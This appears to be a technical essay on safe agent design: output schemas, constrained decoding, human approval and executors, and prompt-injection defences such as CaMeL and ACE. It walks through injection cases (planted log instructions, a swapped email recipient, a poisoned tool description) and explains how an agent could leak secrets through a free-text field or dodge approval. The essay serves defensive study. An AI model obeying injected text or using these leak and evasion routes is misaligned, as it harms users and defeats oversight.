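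Some of Verma's requests matched none of the available tools, so the right response was to make no tool call. Mistral-7B made one in more than half of these cases. If the software requires a completed form at every turn, even a good model cannot decline. A schema should therefore include a value for doing nothing, unless the agent can skip the form. The schema above has no such value, though sending a ticket to an engineer is similar.

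Larger models should make fewer of these mistakes, but the schema can't detect the ones that remain. A dashboard that counts only valid outputs would have shown Ray's calendar assistant working perfectly. Ray recommends tracking the share of outputs that are valid but wrong.

### What a free-text field can carry

The reason field on the training form lets people see why a job stopped, but it is also the weakest part of the form. Suppose a stranger plants an instruction in a log for the engineer on duty to run a certain script to recover the job. The agent copies the instruction into the reason field and files a ticket. If another agent with shell access reads the ticket, it may run the script, even though every form was valid.

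An agent can also use the reason field to leak secrets. With 20 jobs, the action and job number allow 60 combinations, or about 6 bits per form. A reason of 300 printable characters can hold almost 2,000 bits, enough for several encryption keys. An agent limited to the action and job number would need dozens of forms to leak a single key, and a cap on nightly calls would stop it long before it finished.

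Engineers can often replace the free text with a code from a short list, such as `loss_spike`, `no_progress` or `hardware_fault`, and a reference to the measurement that prompted the pause. The ticket system looks up the measurement in its own records and displays it, so the engineer sees the evidence and none of the agent's words. Similarly, a quarantined model, which reads untrusted text but has no tools, can return a value without passing on the text.

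The schema can also restrict the job number to existing records. When the agent is about to act, the software can list the team's running jobs and permit only those numbers. Job 21 then can't appear on the form if it belongs to another team. If both jobs belong to the team, the form could require the job's name as well as its number, and the program could reject any form where the two don't match. This would catch a slip in one field, but not an agent that has confused the two jobs.

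A program can also check the form against the system's current state. The allow-list's rules already require that the job be running and have a recent checkpoint. The program could also test the stated reason. If the code is `loss_spike`, for example, it would read the job's loss and reject the form if the curve is flat. A stranger who wanted to pause healthy runs would then have to falsify the measurements, not just the log.

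Narrower fields may also make the model more accurate. In *Constrained Decoding*, Nguyen, Silva and colleagues (2026) used a puzzle whose answer always has the same number of letters, and a schema that permitted only answers of that length. Limits like this raised accuracy by up to 17.4 percent and helped more consistently than enforcing the format alone. The limits must be correct, because the model cannot give an answer that the schema excludes.

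### What formats cost in accuracy

The dispute over whether strict output formats harm performance began with *Let Me Speak Freely?* (Tam, Wu and colleagues, 2024), which found that they may hinder reasoning but can help with classification. Gemini 1.5 Flash, for instance, did much better in JSON mode on a medical diagnosis dataset, perhaps because the format limited the possible answers. dottxt, a company that develops software for constrained decoding, published a reply that year, which Nguyen and colleagues cite for the view that the comparison of constrained and unconstrained answers was unfair.

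Researchers still disagree about why structured output can lower scores on reasoning benchmarks. Lee and colleagues compared the same prompt with and without constrained decoding, using six open-weight models, three reasoning benchmarks and four formats. The format made a statistically significant difference in 39 of the 72 combinations. In 36 of those, the difference appeared when the prompt only asked for the format, and in the other three it came from constrained decoding alone. Asking for the format lowered scores by 3.9 percentage points on average, and enforcing it lowered them by 1.6.

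Verma found the reverse on school mathematics problems. Asking for JSON changed accuracy by only a few points, and improved it for two of three models. Enforcing the format lowered accuracy by 1.2 points for Qwen3-8B and 25.3 points for Llama-3.1-8B.

Nguyen and colleagues argue that constrained decoding can't do harm if everything else stays the same. Their proof follows from the formula above. Masking divides the probability of a valid answer Y by the feasible mass at every step:

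q(Y) = p(Y) / (α₁ · α₂ · … · αₙ)

Each α is at most one, so the probability of the right answer cannot fall. In experiments on eleven open models, constrained decoding matched or beat free decoding when the prompt and the expected format were the same.

The proof holds the model's reasoning fixed and counts an answer as wrong if it is not in the required format. It therefore doesn't cover errors that occur because the format leaves the model no room to work through the problem. Reddy and colleagues, for example, asked a model to solve 3(2x − 1) = 81 and to reply only with a JSON object containing the answer. The model gave 27, which is the value of 2x − 1. When it could first write a free draft, it gave the correct answer, 14.

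This may also explain some of the conflict between the measurements. Lee and colleagues' schemas included a field for reasoning, so the models could write out their working within the structured output. A model that is asked for JSON but not constrained to it can still write out its working first, but a grammar that applies from the first token may prevent that. The starkest case is in *Capacity, Not Format* (Fan, 2026), where GPT-4o-mini solved 60 percent of a set of hard mathematics problems in free text, but 10 percent when it had to answer immediately with a function call. When the function call was optional, it mostly answered in text and solved 57 percent. Ray's calendar doesn't fit this explanation, because copying "30 minutes" into a field takes no working.

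Fan's main finding is that the accuracy a model loses by answering in JSON depends on how close the task is to the limit of the model's ability. The table gives accuracy in free text and in JSON. Fan only asked for JSON in the prompt, while Verma enforced it.

| Source | Model and task | Free text | JSON |
|---|---|---|---|
| Fan | Claude Sonnet 4.6, hard mathematics | 89.3% | 88.7% |
| Fan | Claude Haiku 4.5, hard mathematics | 88.7% | 52.5% |
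| Fan | GPT-4o-mini, hard mathematics | 62.3% | 34.3% |
| Fan | Claude Opus 4.7, AIME competition problems | 96.2% | 91.0% |
| Verma | Qwen3-8B, school mathematics | 90.9% | 93.9% |
| Verma | Llama-3.1-8B, school mathematics | 83.9% | 55.2% |

Haiku's loss came largely from answers that ran out of space, because Fan's JSON form required a lot of text. GPT-4o-mini's loss remained when it had four times as much space. Opus 4.7 lost seven problems out of 133, which is weak evidence that the strongest models also do worse. Lee and colleagues found that newer closed models lost almost nothing when the prompt asked for a format. GPT-5.4 nano was an odd exception when the format was enforced. It lost 59 points on mathematics when constrained to XML, another text format, because it wrote placeholder answers instead of calculating. It had no such trouble with JSON.

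Researchers largely agree on the remedy, which is to let the model reason freely and fill in the form afterwards. In Fan's tests, this recovered about 80 percent of Haiku's loss. Reddy and colleagues used it to raise a one-billion-parameter model's score on school mathematics from 15.2 to 39.0 percent. Filling in the form with a second call to the model roughly doubles the number of tokens, but *Thinking Before Constraining* (2026) presents a method that switches to the constrained format within a single answer and adds only 5 to 20 tokens. When the switch came too early and cut the reasoning short, accuracy on school mathematics fell by over 30 percent. The masking itself slows the model only modestly, by 5 to 27 percent in Verma's measurements.

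An agent loop usually gives the model room to reason already, since the model can write text before it calls a tool. The agent that watches training jobs can reason at length about a loss curve and then fill in three short fields. The software should pass on only those fields, because the reasoning is also free text and may repeat whatever the agent read in the logs.

### Agents that write code instead

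Some developers have moved in the opposite direction and let agents act by writing programs. CodeAct (2024) was an early example. *The Bitter Lesson of Tool Calling* (Patel, Sen and colleagues, 2026) reports that CodeAct achieved up to 20 percent higher success than JSON calls on tasks with several tools, in 30 percent fewer turns.

The argument became more practical once agents had hundreds of tools. Many of these reach the agent through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a standard Anthropic launched in 2024 for connecting agents to tools and data. Anthropic's *Code execution with MCP* explains that the descriptions of all the tools and every intermediate result pass through the model's context, the text it processes at each step. Anthropic's *Introducing advanced tool use on the Claude Developer Platform* reports that together they can take up more than 50,000 tokens before the agent reads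 a request. If the agent writes a script instead, the script can call the tools, filter the results and return only a short answer. *Thoughts on Anthropic's Code Execution Article* (Miessler, 2025) quotes Anthropic's figure of a reduction from 150,000 tokens to 2,000.

*Beyond Plain MCP* (Rai, 2026) compared scripts with JSON calls on 119 simulated office tasks, using 42 tools and three open-weight models. Scripts used 70 to 90 percent fewer tokens. With scripts, success rose from 85.7 to 99.2 percent for Qwen3.8-27B and from 36.1 to 55.5 percent for Nemotron 3 Nano, while Gemma 4 showed no clear change. Without information about what each tool would return, Nemotron's success with scripts fell to 16.0 percent and Gemma's fell from 89.1 to 66.4 percent, both worse than with JSON calls. A model has to anticipate the results when it writes a script, instead of reading each one before making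 the next call.

Patel and colleagues compared tool calls written as code and as JSON on 14 models, and code did at least as well on 11 of them. GPT-5.6 Sol improved from 72.2 percent with JSON to 82.8 percent with code. Three older GPT models lost 20 to 27 points with code because they wrote line breaks in a way that crashed their scripts. Code also did better on very large batches. Claude Sonnet 5 began to drop JSON calls when a task needed about 70 at once, but issued all 100 when it wrote a script. The tools were dummies that returned their own inputs, so the test measured how well the models write calls, not how well they use the results.

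For coding agents, the choice seems to affect cost more than success. *When Does Restricting a Coding Agent to execute_code Help?* (Yang, Yu and Desell, 2026) replaced all the tools of Claude Code and Codex with a single one that runs code. Success rates changed by less than three percentage points. Costs fell by 25 percent for Claude Code on computation tasks and by 20 percent for Codex on software repairs, with no significant change in the other two cases. The agents also had a shell in the ordinary set-up, so the experiment didn't measure what an agent would lose if it couldn't run code.

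### What an agent loses without code

Suppose the agent that watches training jobs has to check whether the same fault affects all 20 runs. With forms alone, it must request each run's measurements in turn and compare all the numbers by reading them. A short script could fetch all the measurements, line up the curves and report the three that diverge. Forms alone also rule out any analysis their designers didn't foresee. In Kitchin's laboratory example, one line of Python measures the lamp at five levels of green, and a few more lines fit a model to the results and choose the next setting.

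The capabilities that a structured form rules out are also useful to an attacker. *From Tool Orchestration to Code Execution* (2026) notes that generated programs can manipulate strings, branch, and build and execute new code as they run, none of which a call bound to a schema can do. A tool's output can also enter the running program without going through any check on the parameters. A reviewer can read a three-field form in a few seconds but may need to trace a script line by line to learn what it will do.

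A system can keep much of the benefit of code if scripts can affect the outside world only through forms. The agent's script runs in a sandbox without credentials or network access. It can call the listed tools, and a program outside the sandbox validates each call against its schema and the allow-list, as if the model had made it directly. The agent could then analyse all 20 loss curves in code but would still have to submit a form to pause a job. The sandbox is essential because a script that escapes it is no longer limited to the forms. Limits on the number of calls also matter more, since a loop can submit hundreds of valid forms before anyone notices the first.

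## Separating recommendation from action

An agent that fills in valid forms may still be able to act without them. If the password for the job system is on the machine where the agent runs, the agent can find it and skip the form, much as the agent at PocketOS found a token in an unrelated file. Separating recommendation from action prevents this. The agent writes a proposal for an action it cannot carry out itself. A reviewer, which can be a person, another model or a fixed program, accepts or rejects the proposal. An executor, the component that holds the credentials, carries out accepted proposals.

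Recommendation is separate from action when the component that recommends has no credential that would let it act. To check this, an engineer lists every password, key and token that the agent's process can read or use, and determines whether any of them could produce the effect in question. The answer can differ between effects. For example, an agent that watches training jobs may have a credential for the ticket queue but none for the job system, so it can file tickets itself but can only recommend pausing a job.

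### Asking first, and only advising

Telling an agent to ask before acting does not separate recommendation from action if the agent can still act without approval. In *Separation of Duties for Privileged LLM Agents*, Jing (2026) told three models to require approval before any dangerous operation, then had each judge 150 requests five times. The models permitted 78.1 percent of the dangerous operations. The figure is high partly because Jing counted a request for confirmation as permission, assuming that an agent working alone might confirm its own request. An attentive person would have stopped some of these operations. When Jing repeated a request under the same settings, the five answers agreed only 49 to 71 percent of the time, depending on the model.

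Software can enforce the pause instead. *Reframing LLM Agent Security as an Agent-Human Interaction Problem* (2026) describes products that halt the agent until a person approves, edits or rejects the next action. This is more reliable than instructing the model to pause, because the model might ignore the instruction. But if the halted process also holds the credentials, a script that the agent started earlier might still use them without approval.

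A purely advisory system passes the test but has no executor. The agent writes "pause job 12" in a report, and an engineer who agrees types the command, perhaps with the wrong job number. In a system with a separate executor, the accepted proposal is the executor's input, so nobody retypes it. In its *Safe Outputs MCP Gateway Specification* (2026), GitHub objects that advisory roles give up the benefits of automation and that manual approval of everything creates bottlenecks. Its design is meant to avoid both problems.

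### GitHub's safe outputs, stage by stage

GitHub Agentic Workflows lets developers describe a recurring task in ordinary language, such as sorting bug reports, and have an agent perform it on a schedule or when something happens in a project. Khelifi, Oukhay and colleagues (2026), in *Specifying and Maintaining Agentic Workflows*, collected 1,248 of these workflow files from 276 projects. Each file combines instructions for the agent with settings for the software around it. The settings for an agent that may only open issues, GitHub's version of tickets, could look like this:

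```
permissions:
  contents: read       # the agent may read the code
safe-outputs:
  create-issue:        # the only change it may request
    max: 3             # no more than three per run
```

In GitHub's *Under the hood*, the company assumes that an agent will try to read and write things it shouldn't. It therefore divides each run into stages:

1. A compiler turns the file into separate jobs. The agent's job receives a read-only token, and a firewall restricts its network access. The keys for the language model and other services stay in containers that the agent can't enter.
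2. When the agent wants to open an issue, it calls a tool named `create_issue`. The tool checks the fields against a schema and adds the request to a file as one line of JSON. It returns an identifier, which confirms only that the tool recorded the request.
3. The agent's job ends, and GitHub's storage passes the file to the next job.
4. A model looks for prompt injection, leaked secrets and malicious code in the agent's output. According to GitHub's *Threat Detection*, nothing goes further if the model finds a threat or if the check itself breaks down. The author of the workflow can switch this stage off.
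5. A fixed program checks the number of requests of each kind, cleans the text, removes links to unapproved sites if the author has listed approved ones, and checks which project each request would change. If the agent asks for four issues and the limit is three, the program rejects all four.
6. A job with permission to write issues creates them.

An agent controlled by an attacker could still open three misleading issues, and GitHub acknowledges that plausible but inappropriate content within the limits is a remaining risk. The agent could not merge code or delete a branch, because its token doesn't permit either and the file declares no such output.

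Code changes are handled similarly. In GitHub's *Safe Outputs (Pull Requests)*, the agent edits its own copy of the project, and the software exports the edits as a patch, a file that lists the changed lines. A separate job applies the patch to a new branch and opens a pull request. Khelifi and colleagues describe how Microsoft's .NET runtime project uses this process. One agent looks for failed tests every 12 hours and files issues about them. Another reads those issues, attempts repairs and opens draft pull requests for people to review.

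Whether a workflow separates recommendation from action depends on its permission settings. One workflow file that Khelifi and colleagues reproduce requests permission to write issues alongside its safe outputs. If the agent's job receives that permission, the agent can change issues directly, and the separation is lost. GitHub also offers a permission called `id-token: write`, which does not allow changes to the project but lets a workflow request short-lived credentials for cloud services such as Amazon's. An agent with this permission and read-only access to the code could still delete a server if the cloud account allows the workflow to do so.

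### Acceptance without a person

None of the six stages requires a human decision. GitHub's glossary defines safe outputs as "pre-approved actions", and its *Safe Outputs* warns that some configurations publish content or merge pull requests automatically. An older guide, GitHub Next's *Security Best Practices*, said these workflows could not approve or merge pull requests. GitHub has since added merging as an experimental output, and the merge goes through once the project's policy checks pass.

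Workflow authors who want a person involved have to arrange it. They can require manual approval or make every pull request a draft, a setting the agent can't override. GitHub describes a code-tidying workflow, jsweep, whose pull requests are always drafts and expire after two days. Authors can also run a workflow in a preview mode that shows what it would have changed.

### Running exactly what the reviewer accepted

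Moving the credentials to an executor achieves little if the agent can influence what the executor does after the decision. Kodathala, Pollishetty and Cargill (2026), in *Approve What, Exactly?*, give two conditions that an approval must meet to protect anything. An attacker who controls the agent must be unable to produce the approval, and the approval must commit to exactly the action that runs. They take the second condition from European payment rules, which tie a payer's confirmation code to the amount and the recipient, so that the code stops working if either changes.

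Software can enforce this with a hash, a short fingerprint of a text that changes when the text does:

h = H(C(a))

The fingerprint of a proposed action a is h = H(C(a)), where C converts the action to a standard form, so that the same action always produces the same text, and H computes the fingerprint of that text. The reviewer's acceptance contains h. Before the executor runs an action a′, it computes H(C(a′)) and refuses to run the action if the result differs from h. If the agent changes "job 12" to "job 21" after the decision, the fingerprints don't match and the changed action needs a new decision.

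The fingerprint must cover everything that determines the effect. For the training form, the action and the job number are enough. If the proposal is to run a script, the fingerprint must include the script's contents. The first version of Jing's system checked the fingerprint of the request but not of the file it referred to, so an attacker could have a harmless script accepted and then replace it. Jing tried seven such swaps, and two deleted a test file. None of the seven ran after Jing made the executor check the file itself. In a larger set of tests, this check raised the share of blocked tampering from 61.3 to 90.3 percent.

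An acceptance must also work only once. *Context-to-Execution Integrity for LLM Agents* (2026) requires authority for the choice of tool, for its sensitive values and for the particular occasion, so permission to pause job 12 tonight does not cover pausing it again tomorrow. At one stage, Jing's system blocked only 77.8 percent of attempts to reuse an acceptance, but this rose to 100 percent when the executor began to record each acceptance as used.

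These faults also occur in widely available software. Kodathala and colleagues audited ten systems for running agents. Of the eight they could test for this problem, four allowed the action to change between approval and execution. Agents that use a browser face the same problem, because a web page can replace the recipient of a payment after the user clicks "approve". *The Verifiable Action Card* (2026) presents a system that compares the recipient and amount in the outgoing request with the approved values and asks the user to approve again if they differ.

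The reviewer also has to see the action that will run. In one of Kodathala and colleagues' tests, an agent was supposed to email a report to the user's boss, but it added a hidden copy to an outside address and left this out of its description. Fifteen language models reviewed the email based on that description, and all approved it. When trusted software wrote the description from the actual tool call, all fifteen refused.

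### Stale proposals and protected limits

A correct decision can become wrong while the proposed action waits. Shraga, Eshel and Gorelik (2026), in *Approved Too Late*, measured this in five simulated systems. They applied a fixed rule to each proposed action, and again eight simulation steps later. The verdict had changed in 5.3 percent of cases in a system that sends jobs to servers, and in 48.4 percent in a wireless sensor network. Some of those changes were from unacceptable to acceptable, but between 3.4 and 24.7 percent of the actions that the rule had correctly approved were no longer acceptable.

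Shraga and colleagues give each approval a lifetime based on how close the system is to the limit and how fast it has been moving. Leaving out the caps that they add, the lifetime is:

δ = m / v

The margin m is the distance to the limit, and v is the recent rate of change. For example, the training agent may pause a job only if its last checkpoint is less than 30 minutes old. If the checkpoint is 22 minutes old, the margin is 8 minutes. The checkpoint ages one minute per minute, so v is 1 and the proposal is valid for 8 minutes. For a quantity like the loss, v is an estimate, and a sudden jump can invalidate an approval before it expires. In the simulations, this method reduced the share of expired approvals to between 0 and 1.8 percent, but that figure doesn't measure how many valid approvals the method also discarded.

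Decisions that rest on judgement need an expiry time. An executor can recheck the age of a checkpoint before it acts, but it can't repeat an engineer's earlier judgement that a loss curve looked hopeless.

If other people have edited the code since the agent started, GitHub's executor tries to combine their edits with the patch. If the two conflict, it opens the pull request against the older version and leaves the conflict for a person to resolve. Neither the agent nor the model that checked the patch has necessarily seen the combined code. This is acceptable as long as somebody reviews the pull request afterwards.

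The agent must also not be able to edit the rules for accepting proposals. By default, GitHub blocks patches that change workflow files, the agent's standing instructions or the lists of outside software a project uses. Jing keeps the rules, the program that applies them and the record of decisions where the agent can't write. This boundary also needs testing. When Jing switched off the sandbox for a comparison, two test commands reached the live system through a network share and deleted a protected file.

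Agents can still propose changes to their own rules. In the .NET project, a third agent reviews the work of the other two and suggests edits to their instructions. After people rejected an attempted repair to a cryptography test, the third agent proposed sending such cases to the specialists responsible. People reviewed and merged the edit, which then applied to later runs.

### A pause, from proposal to execution

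Suppose the loss of training job 12 jumps at 02:08. The agent can read measurements and logs but has no credential for the job system.

1. At 02:10, the agent submits a form with the action "pause", the job number 12 and the reason code `loss_spike`.
2. A recorder that the agent can't edit stores the form and its fingerprint. It adds the time of the last checkpoint, 01:48, and sets the proposal to expire at 02:18.
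3. A fixed program applies the allow-list's rules for pausing and confirms the jump in the measurement system.
4. The team has approved up to three such pauses a night in advance, so the program accepts the proposal. It could send a fourth to the engineer on duty instead of refusing it.
5. The executor compares the fingerprints, checks the time and the job's state again, pauses the job with its own credential and marks the proposal as used.
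6. The agent learns the result by reading the job's status.

If the agent meant job 21, it can't amend the stored form and has to submit another. If an engineer accepts a proposal at 02:25, the executor won't carry it out, and the agent must propose the pause again using current information.

### The argument and its premises

The case for separation is that it prevents unauthorised action. The argument needs four premises:

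1. The agent can produce the effect only through the executor.
2. The executor runs only accepted proposals, exactly as the reviewer accepted them, and only while the acceptance is valid.
3. Each acceptance is a decision by somebody entitled to make it, and the agent can't produce one itself.
4. Nothing that the agent can do without an acceptance needs authorisation.

If all four are true, no unauthorised action takes place. An authorised action can still be a mistake, since a person entitled to accept proposals may accept a bad one.

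An agent that can run commands can often cause an effect through routes that nobody listed. Jing tested 117 disguised commands, such as ones that used an unusual form of a file's path. When the agent's commands ran directly, 98.3 percent of the attacks succeeded. A separate executor and a program that reviewed each action reduced this to 30.8 percent, and adding an operating-system sandbox reduced it to 7.7 percent. The 7.7 percent figure comes from a model of the sandbox. In the real sandbox, 5 of the 66 commands that Jing could evaluate took effect, including one that deleted a file on another drive. The full system also refused 6 of 54 ordinary tasks, because the sandbox allowed writing in fewer places than the rules did. The premise that the executor is the only route therefore depends heavily on the sandbox, as well as on where the credentials are.

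An agent proposes a code change in a pull request, the tests pass and a separate job merges it automatically. The agent never had permission to merge, so the system passes the test for separation. But nobody decided on this particular change. The workflow's author decided in advance to accept any change that passes the checks, which fits poorly with the premise that an entitled person decides on each acceptance. This matters more when the approved class is broad, because a rule that admits any code that passes the tests leaves far more undecided than one that admits only spelling corrections in documentation. The agent might also weaken a test in the same patch, since GitHub's default list of protected files does not cover ordinary tests. Workflow authors can prevent this by listing the only files a patch may change.

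Merging code also weakens the assumption that the agent has no other way to cause an effect. Merged code may later run with the company's production credentials, so whoever approves a merge is also accepting whatever the code does with those credentials.

Suppose an engineer has accepted all 500 of an agent's proposals. The agent may be excellent, or the engineer may have stopped reading them, and the record alone doesn't show which. If the engineer would accept anything, the agent in effect approves its own proposals, and the only protection left in the separation is the executor's fixed checks. For example, if the proposal form has no value for deleting a checkpoint, even an engineer who approves everything can't approve a deletion.

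Using another agent as the reviewer makes this worse. According to an industry analysis cited by Jing, agents can get around the rule that a person may not approve their own request by approving each other's. Two agents running on the same model and reading the same misleading log may well make the same mistake.

An agent's report can persuade a person to take an action that the agent can't take itself. The training agent can't delete checkpoints, but it can file a ticket claiming that the old ones are corrupt and that the engineer should remove them. An engineer who believes the ticket then deletes them with a valid credential and the authority to do so, without involving the executor. The separation fails here because it assumes that the agent's other outputs need no authorisation.

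A report can also do harm without persuading anyone. InfoQ's *Indirect Prompt Injection Exploits GitHub's AI Agent to Leak Private Repository Data* (2026) describes an attack in which the agent revealed private data in a public comment, a type of output its workflow allowed. Filing a ticket or posting a comment should therefore count as an action if it can disclose something or if its readers, who may be other agents, will act on it. In the .NET project, one agent files an issue only as a report, but the next agent treats it as a reason to change code. Using reason codes instead of free text, as on the training form, limits what such reports can contain.

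GitHub carries out an agent's requests after the agent has finished. This suits an agent that files three issues, but not one that must see the result of its first action before choosing the second. Suppose the training agent suspects that job 12 is overloading a storage system it shares with job 14. The agent plans to pause job 12, wait ten minutes, and resume job 12 if job 14 has not recovered.

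GitHub partly solves this by letting a request name an earlier one that must succeed before it runs. But this checks only whether the earlier request succeeded, while the training agent needs to know what happened to job 14. GitHub also doesn't undo earlier requests when a later one fails.

Another approach is to rehearse actions before running them. *PROVISO* (2026) studies the "commitment point", the moment between an agent proposing an action and the executor running it. If the software can restore a copy of the environment, it tries alternative sequences of actions in the copy, then runs the chosen one in the live environment. This works for a small database, but few companies have a second cluster on which to rehearse a large training run, and a laboratory can't restore a sample it has used up.

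Without a copy, the agent has to propose one step, wait for the executor, read the result and propose the next. A fixed program can review each step almost at once, but a person would have to stay available all night. The engineer could instead accept the whole plan in advance, including the rule for resuming job 12. The executor would then apply that rule to measurements taken after the engineer accepted it. Because the acceptance may no longer be valid by then, the plan needs its own expiry time and a stopping condition, such as a fault in any third job.

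## Keeping untrusted text from choosing the action

If an agent writes its plan before it reads anything untrusted, the untrusted text also can't add steps to the plan. If the plan for job 12 consists of a pause, a ten-minute wait and a rule for resuming, no instruction in a log can add a deletion. Several designs against prompt injection build on this idea and combine all three patterns. The plan acts as an allow-list for a single task, structured output restricts what the agent can take from untrusted text, and the model that reads the text has no tools or credentials.

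Beurer-Kellner and colleagues hold that once an agent has read untrusted text, it must be impossible for that text to trigger an action that harms the system or its surroundings. This principle covers the agent's answers as well as its tool calls, because an answer can also leak data or mislead another agent. They doubt that a general-purpose agent built on current language models can reliably guarantee this, so each of their six designs rules out some tasks in return for protection.

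### Six designs

In the strictest design, the action-selector, the model turns a request into one of a fixed set of actions and never sees the result. A shop's chatbot might send customers a link to their last order or direct them to the password settings. Text in the order can't influence the chatbot because it never reaches the model, although the customer's own message still determines which action the chatbot picks. For the same reason, the chatbot can't answer questions about the order. An agent of this kind couldn't monitor training jobs, because it could never read a log.

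In plan-then-execute, the model commits to a list of tool calls before it sees any results. For example, an agent asked to send today's schedule to the user's boss plans to read the calendar and then send an email to the boss's address. A malicious calendar entry can't add a third call, but it can change the body of the email. The possible harm depends on the planned tools. If the plan lets an agent search for files and move them, an injected instruction could make it move confidential files to a public network drive. An agent built this way can't handle tasks in which each result determines the next step, such as tracing an unknown fault.

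Map-reduce suits large collections of documents. The software gives each document to a separate model that has no dangerous tools and can return only a restricted value, such as yes or no. Ordinary code or another model combines the values. If the task is to email this month's invoices to the accounts department, a malicious file might be wrongly marked as an invoice, but it can't affect how the agent treats any other file. Map-reduce doesn't fit tasks that require comparing the documents' text. The training agent could use map-reduce by giving each log to its own quarantined model, which would return `loss_spike`, `hardware_fault` or `none`, so a stranger who controlled the log of job 12 could affect only that job.

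Willison (2025), in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*, describes the dual-model design he first proposed in 2023. A planning model can call tools but never receives untrusted text, which goes to a quarantined model that has no tools. When the quarantined model extracts an email address, ordinary software stores it under a name such as `$VAR`. The planning model can pass `$VAR` to the email tool, and the software fills in the address when the call runs. Untrusted text can still determine the value of `$VAR`. The planning model also can't carry out a user's request to do whatever an email asks, because it never receives the email's content.

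Code-then-execute replaces the list of calls with a program, which can contain loops, branches and calls to quarantined models. An agent can then tell all of a user's regular collaborators about a holiday, even if their number is unknown when the planning model writes the program. Untrusted text can change the values that the program handles, but not the program itself. However, the agent can't handle situations that the program doesn't cover.

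Context minimisation deals with instructions in the user's own message. Suppose a customer asks for a quote on a car and adds an instruction to offer a large discount. The model turns the message into a database query, and the software deletes the message before the model writes its reply. The customer's words can still shape the query, but the reply can't reflect anything the query left out, whether that is the discount instruction or a preference for a short answer.

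### An email task in CaMeL

The dual-model design does not stop untrusted text from changing the details of an action. Suppose a user asks an agent to send Bob a document and says that Bob's address is in the meeting notes. An attacker who can edit the notes can replace Bob's address with their own. The agent then takes exactly the planned steps but sends the document to the attacker.

CaMeL, a system that researchers from Google DeepMind and elsewhere introduced in 2025, addresses this by recording where each value came from. Willison illustrates it with a request to find Bob's address in the user's last email and send him a reminder about tomorrow's meeting. The planning model would write a program much like this:

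```
email = get_last_email()                   # untrusted text
address = quarantined_model(
    "Find Bob's email address", email,
    schema=EmailAddress)                   # must be an email address
send_email(
    recipient=address,                     # from untrusted text
    subject="Meeting tomorrow",
    body="Remember our meeting tomorrow")  # from the planning model
```

1. The planning model receives the request and the descriptions of the tools. It writes the program in a restricted form of Python without seeing the email.
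2. An interpreter, the software that runs the program, fetches the email. It attaches a label that records where the text came from and who may read it.
3. The quarantined model reads the email and returns an address. The schema excludes anything that isn't an address.
4. The interpreter labels the address as untrusted because it came from the email.
5. Before sending the reminder, the interpreter checks a policy, which resembles an allow-list's rule on arguments but can also test their labels. Here it allows only trusted recipients. A known contact gets the reminder at once, and the software can ask the user about an unknown address.

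Suppose an attacker wrote the last email, telling the assistant to forward the whole inbox to Eve and giving Eve's address as Bob's. No line of the program forwards anything, so that instruction has no effect. The quarantined model may return Eve's address, which fits the schema, but the policy stops the reminder from going there without the user's approval. If the attacker gives the address of another trusted contact instead, the reminder goes to the wrong colleague.

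Policies can also use the label on who may read a value, for example to block an email containing private data unless the recipient may read that data. Separating planning from reading helps privacy too, because a small model on the user's computer can do the reading. Planning requires a capable model, but the company that supplies it need not see any emails.

As with allow-lists, somebody has to write and maintain these policies. The tools also need better documentation. In *Can CaMeLs Talk?*, Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (2026) had to add an exact description of every tool's output, because the planning model writes the code to process that output before the tools run.

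### Checking the whole plan first

CaMeL treats tool descriptions as trusted. In *ACE*, Li, Mallick and colleagues (2026) instead assume that an attacker may have supplied one of the tools. They demonstrated the danger on IsolateGPT, an earlier system that runs each tool in isolation. A user wanted the fare for a journey, and two apps, MetroHail and QuickRide, could each provide one. QuickRide's description included an instruction for the planning model to leave out MetroHail, so the user saw only QuickRide's fare.

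ACE prevents this by keeping the tools' descriptions away from the model that decides the overall plan:

1. The planning model reads only the user's request and, if needed, some trusted background. It invents the tools that it would like to have, such as a file reader and an email sender, and writes a program that uses them.
2. Another model matches each invented tool to an installed one. It judges each pair separately, so QuickRide's description can't count against MetroHail.
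3. A fixed program checks where information would flow and rejects any plan that would send data to a tool without clearance for it.
4. The software runs each tool in its own container with only the permissions it needs, and checks that the output has the expected type.

The check at step 3 gives every tool f a clearance L(f), a set of categories such as personal, financial or medical. Every input x carries a label L(x) of the same kind. For each call, the combined labels of the inputs must lie within the tool's clearance:

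L(x₁) ∪ L(x₂) ∪ … ∪ L(xₙ) ⊆ L(f)

Suppose a plan loads the user's bank details and emails them, but the email tool has clearance only for personal data. The details carry the label {financial}, which is not a subset of {personal}, so ACE rejects the plan before any tool runs. CaMeL would load the details first and stop only at the email.

In another attack on IsolateGPT, QuickRide returned instructions instead of a fare, and the agent reported an inflated fare for MetroHail. ACE showed MetroHail's real fare and a type error for QuickRide. A malicious app could still return a false number, because a number has the right type.

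Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues (2026), in *CaMeLoT*, add an early check to CaMeL. One of their examples is an agent that investigates security alerts and may cut a computer off from the network, but only with approval from the incident response team. If the planning model forgets the approval, CaMeL discovers this at the last step, after a long and possibly expensive investigation. CaMeLoT translates the program into a finite set of states and searches every path through them for one that breaks a rule such as:

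Always(isolated(host) ⇒ approved(host))

If CaMeLoT finds a path through the plan that breaks a rule, it describes the path to the planning model, which tries to repair the plan. The rules can also require that something eventually happens, such as the agent closing every ticket it opens. A policy that checks each call separately can't express this. CaMeLoT may reject some safe plans because of how it simplifies loops.

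### Results and what they measure

Most tests of these designs use AgentDojo. Its current version combines 97 tasks with attacks into 949 test cases, more than half of them in office work, according to *SecOPD* (2026). The benchmark counts the tasks the agent completes and the attackers' goals it carries out, and an agent can do both in the same run. Models had little resistance when AgentDojo appeared in 2024. In the original scores, which *CorrGRPO* (2026) reproduces, nearly half of the attacks succeeded against GPT-4o.

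*SecureClaw* (2026), which proposes a rival system, ran CaMeL on an AgentDojo set with 629 attacks. *The LLMbda Calculus* (Garby, Gordon and Sands, 2026) reran CaMeL on the banking tasks and compared it with the authors' own agent, Randori, which also plans first and tracks where data came from. Task success in the table is measured without an attack, except for ACE.

| Source | Agent and test | Successful attacks | Task success |
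|---|---|---|---|
| *CorrGRPO* | GPT-4o with no defence, AgentDojo | 47.7% | 69.0% |
| *SecureClaw* | CaMeL, AgentDojo | 0 of 629 | 29.9% |
| Garby and colleagues | CaMeL without policies, GPT-5.2, AgentDojo banking | 1 of 240 | 66.7% |
| Garby and colleagues | CaMeL with policies, GPT-5.2, AgentDojo banking | 0 of 231 | 37.5% |
| Garby and colleagues | Randori, GPT-5.2, AgentDojo banking | 2 of 432 | 75.0% |
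| Li and colleagues | ACE, GPT-4o, InjecAgent | 0 of 1,054 | 83.6% |

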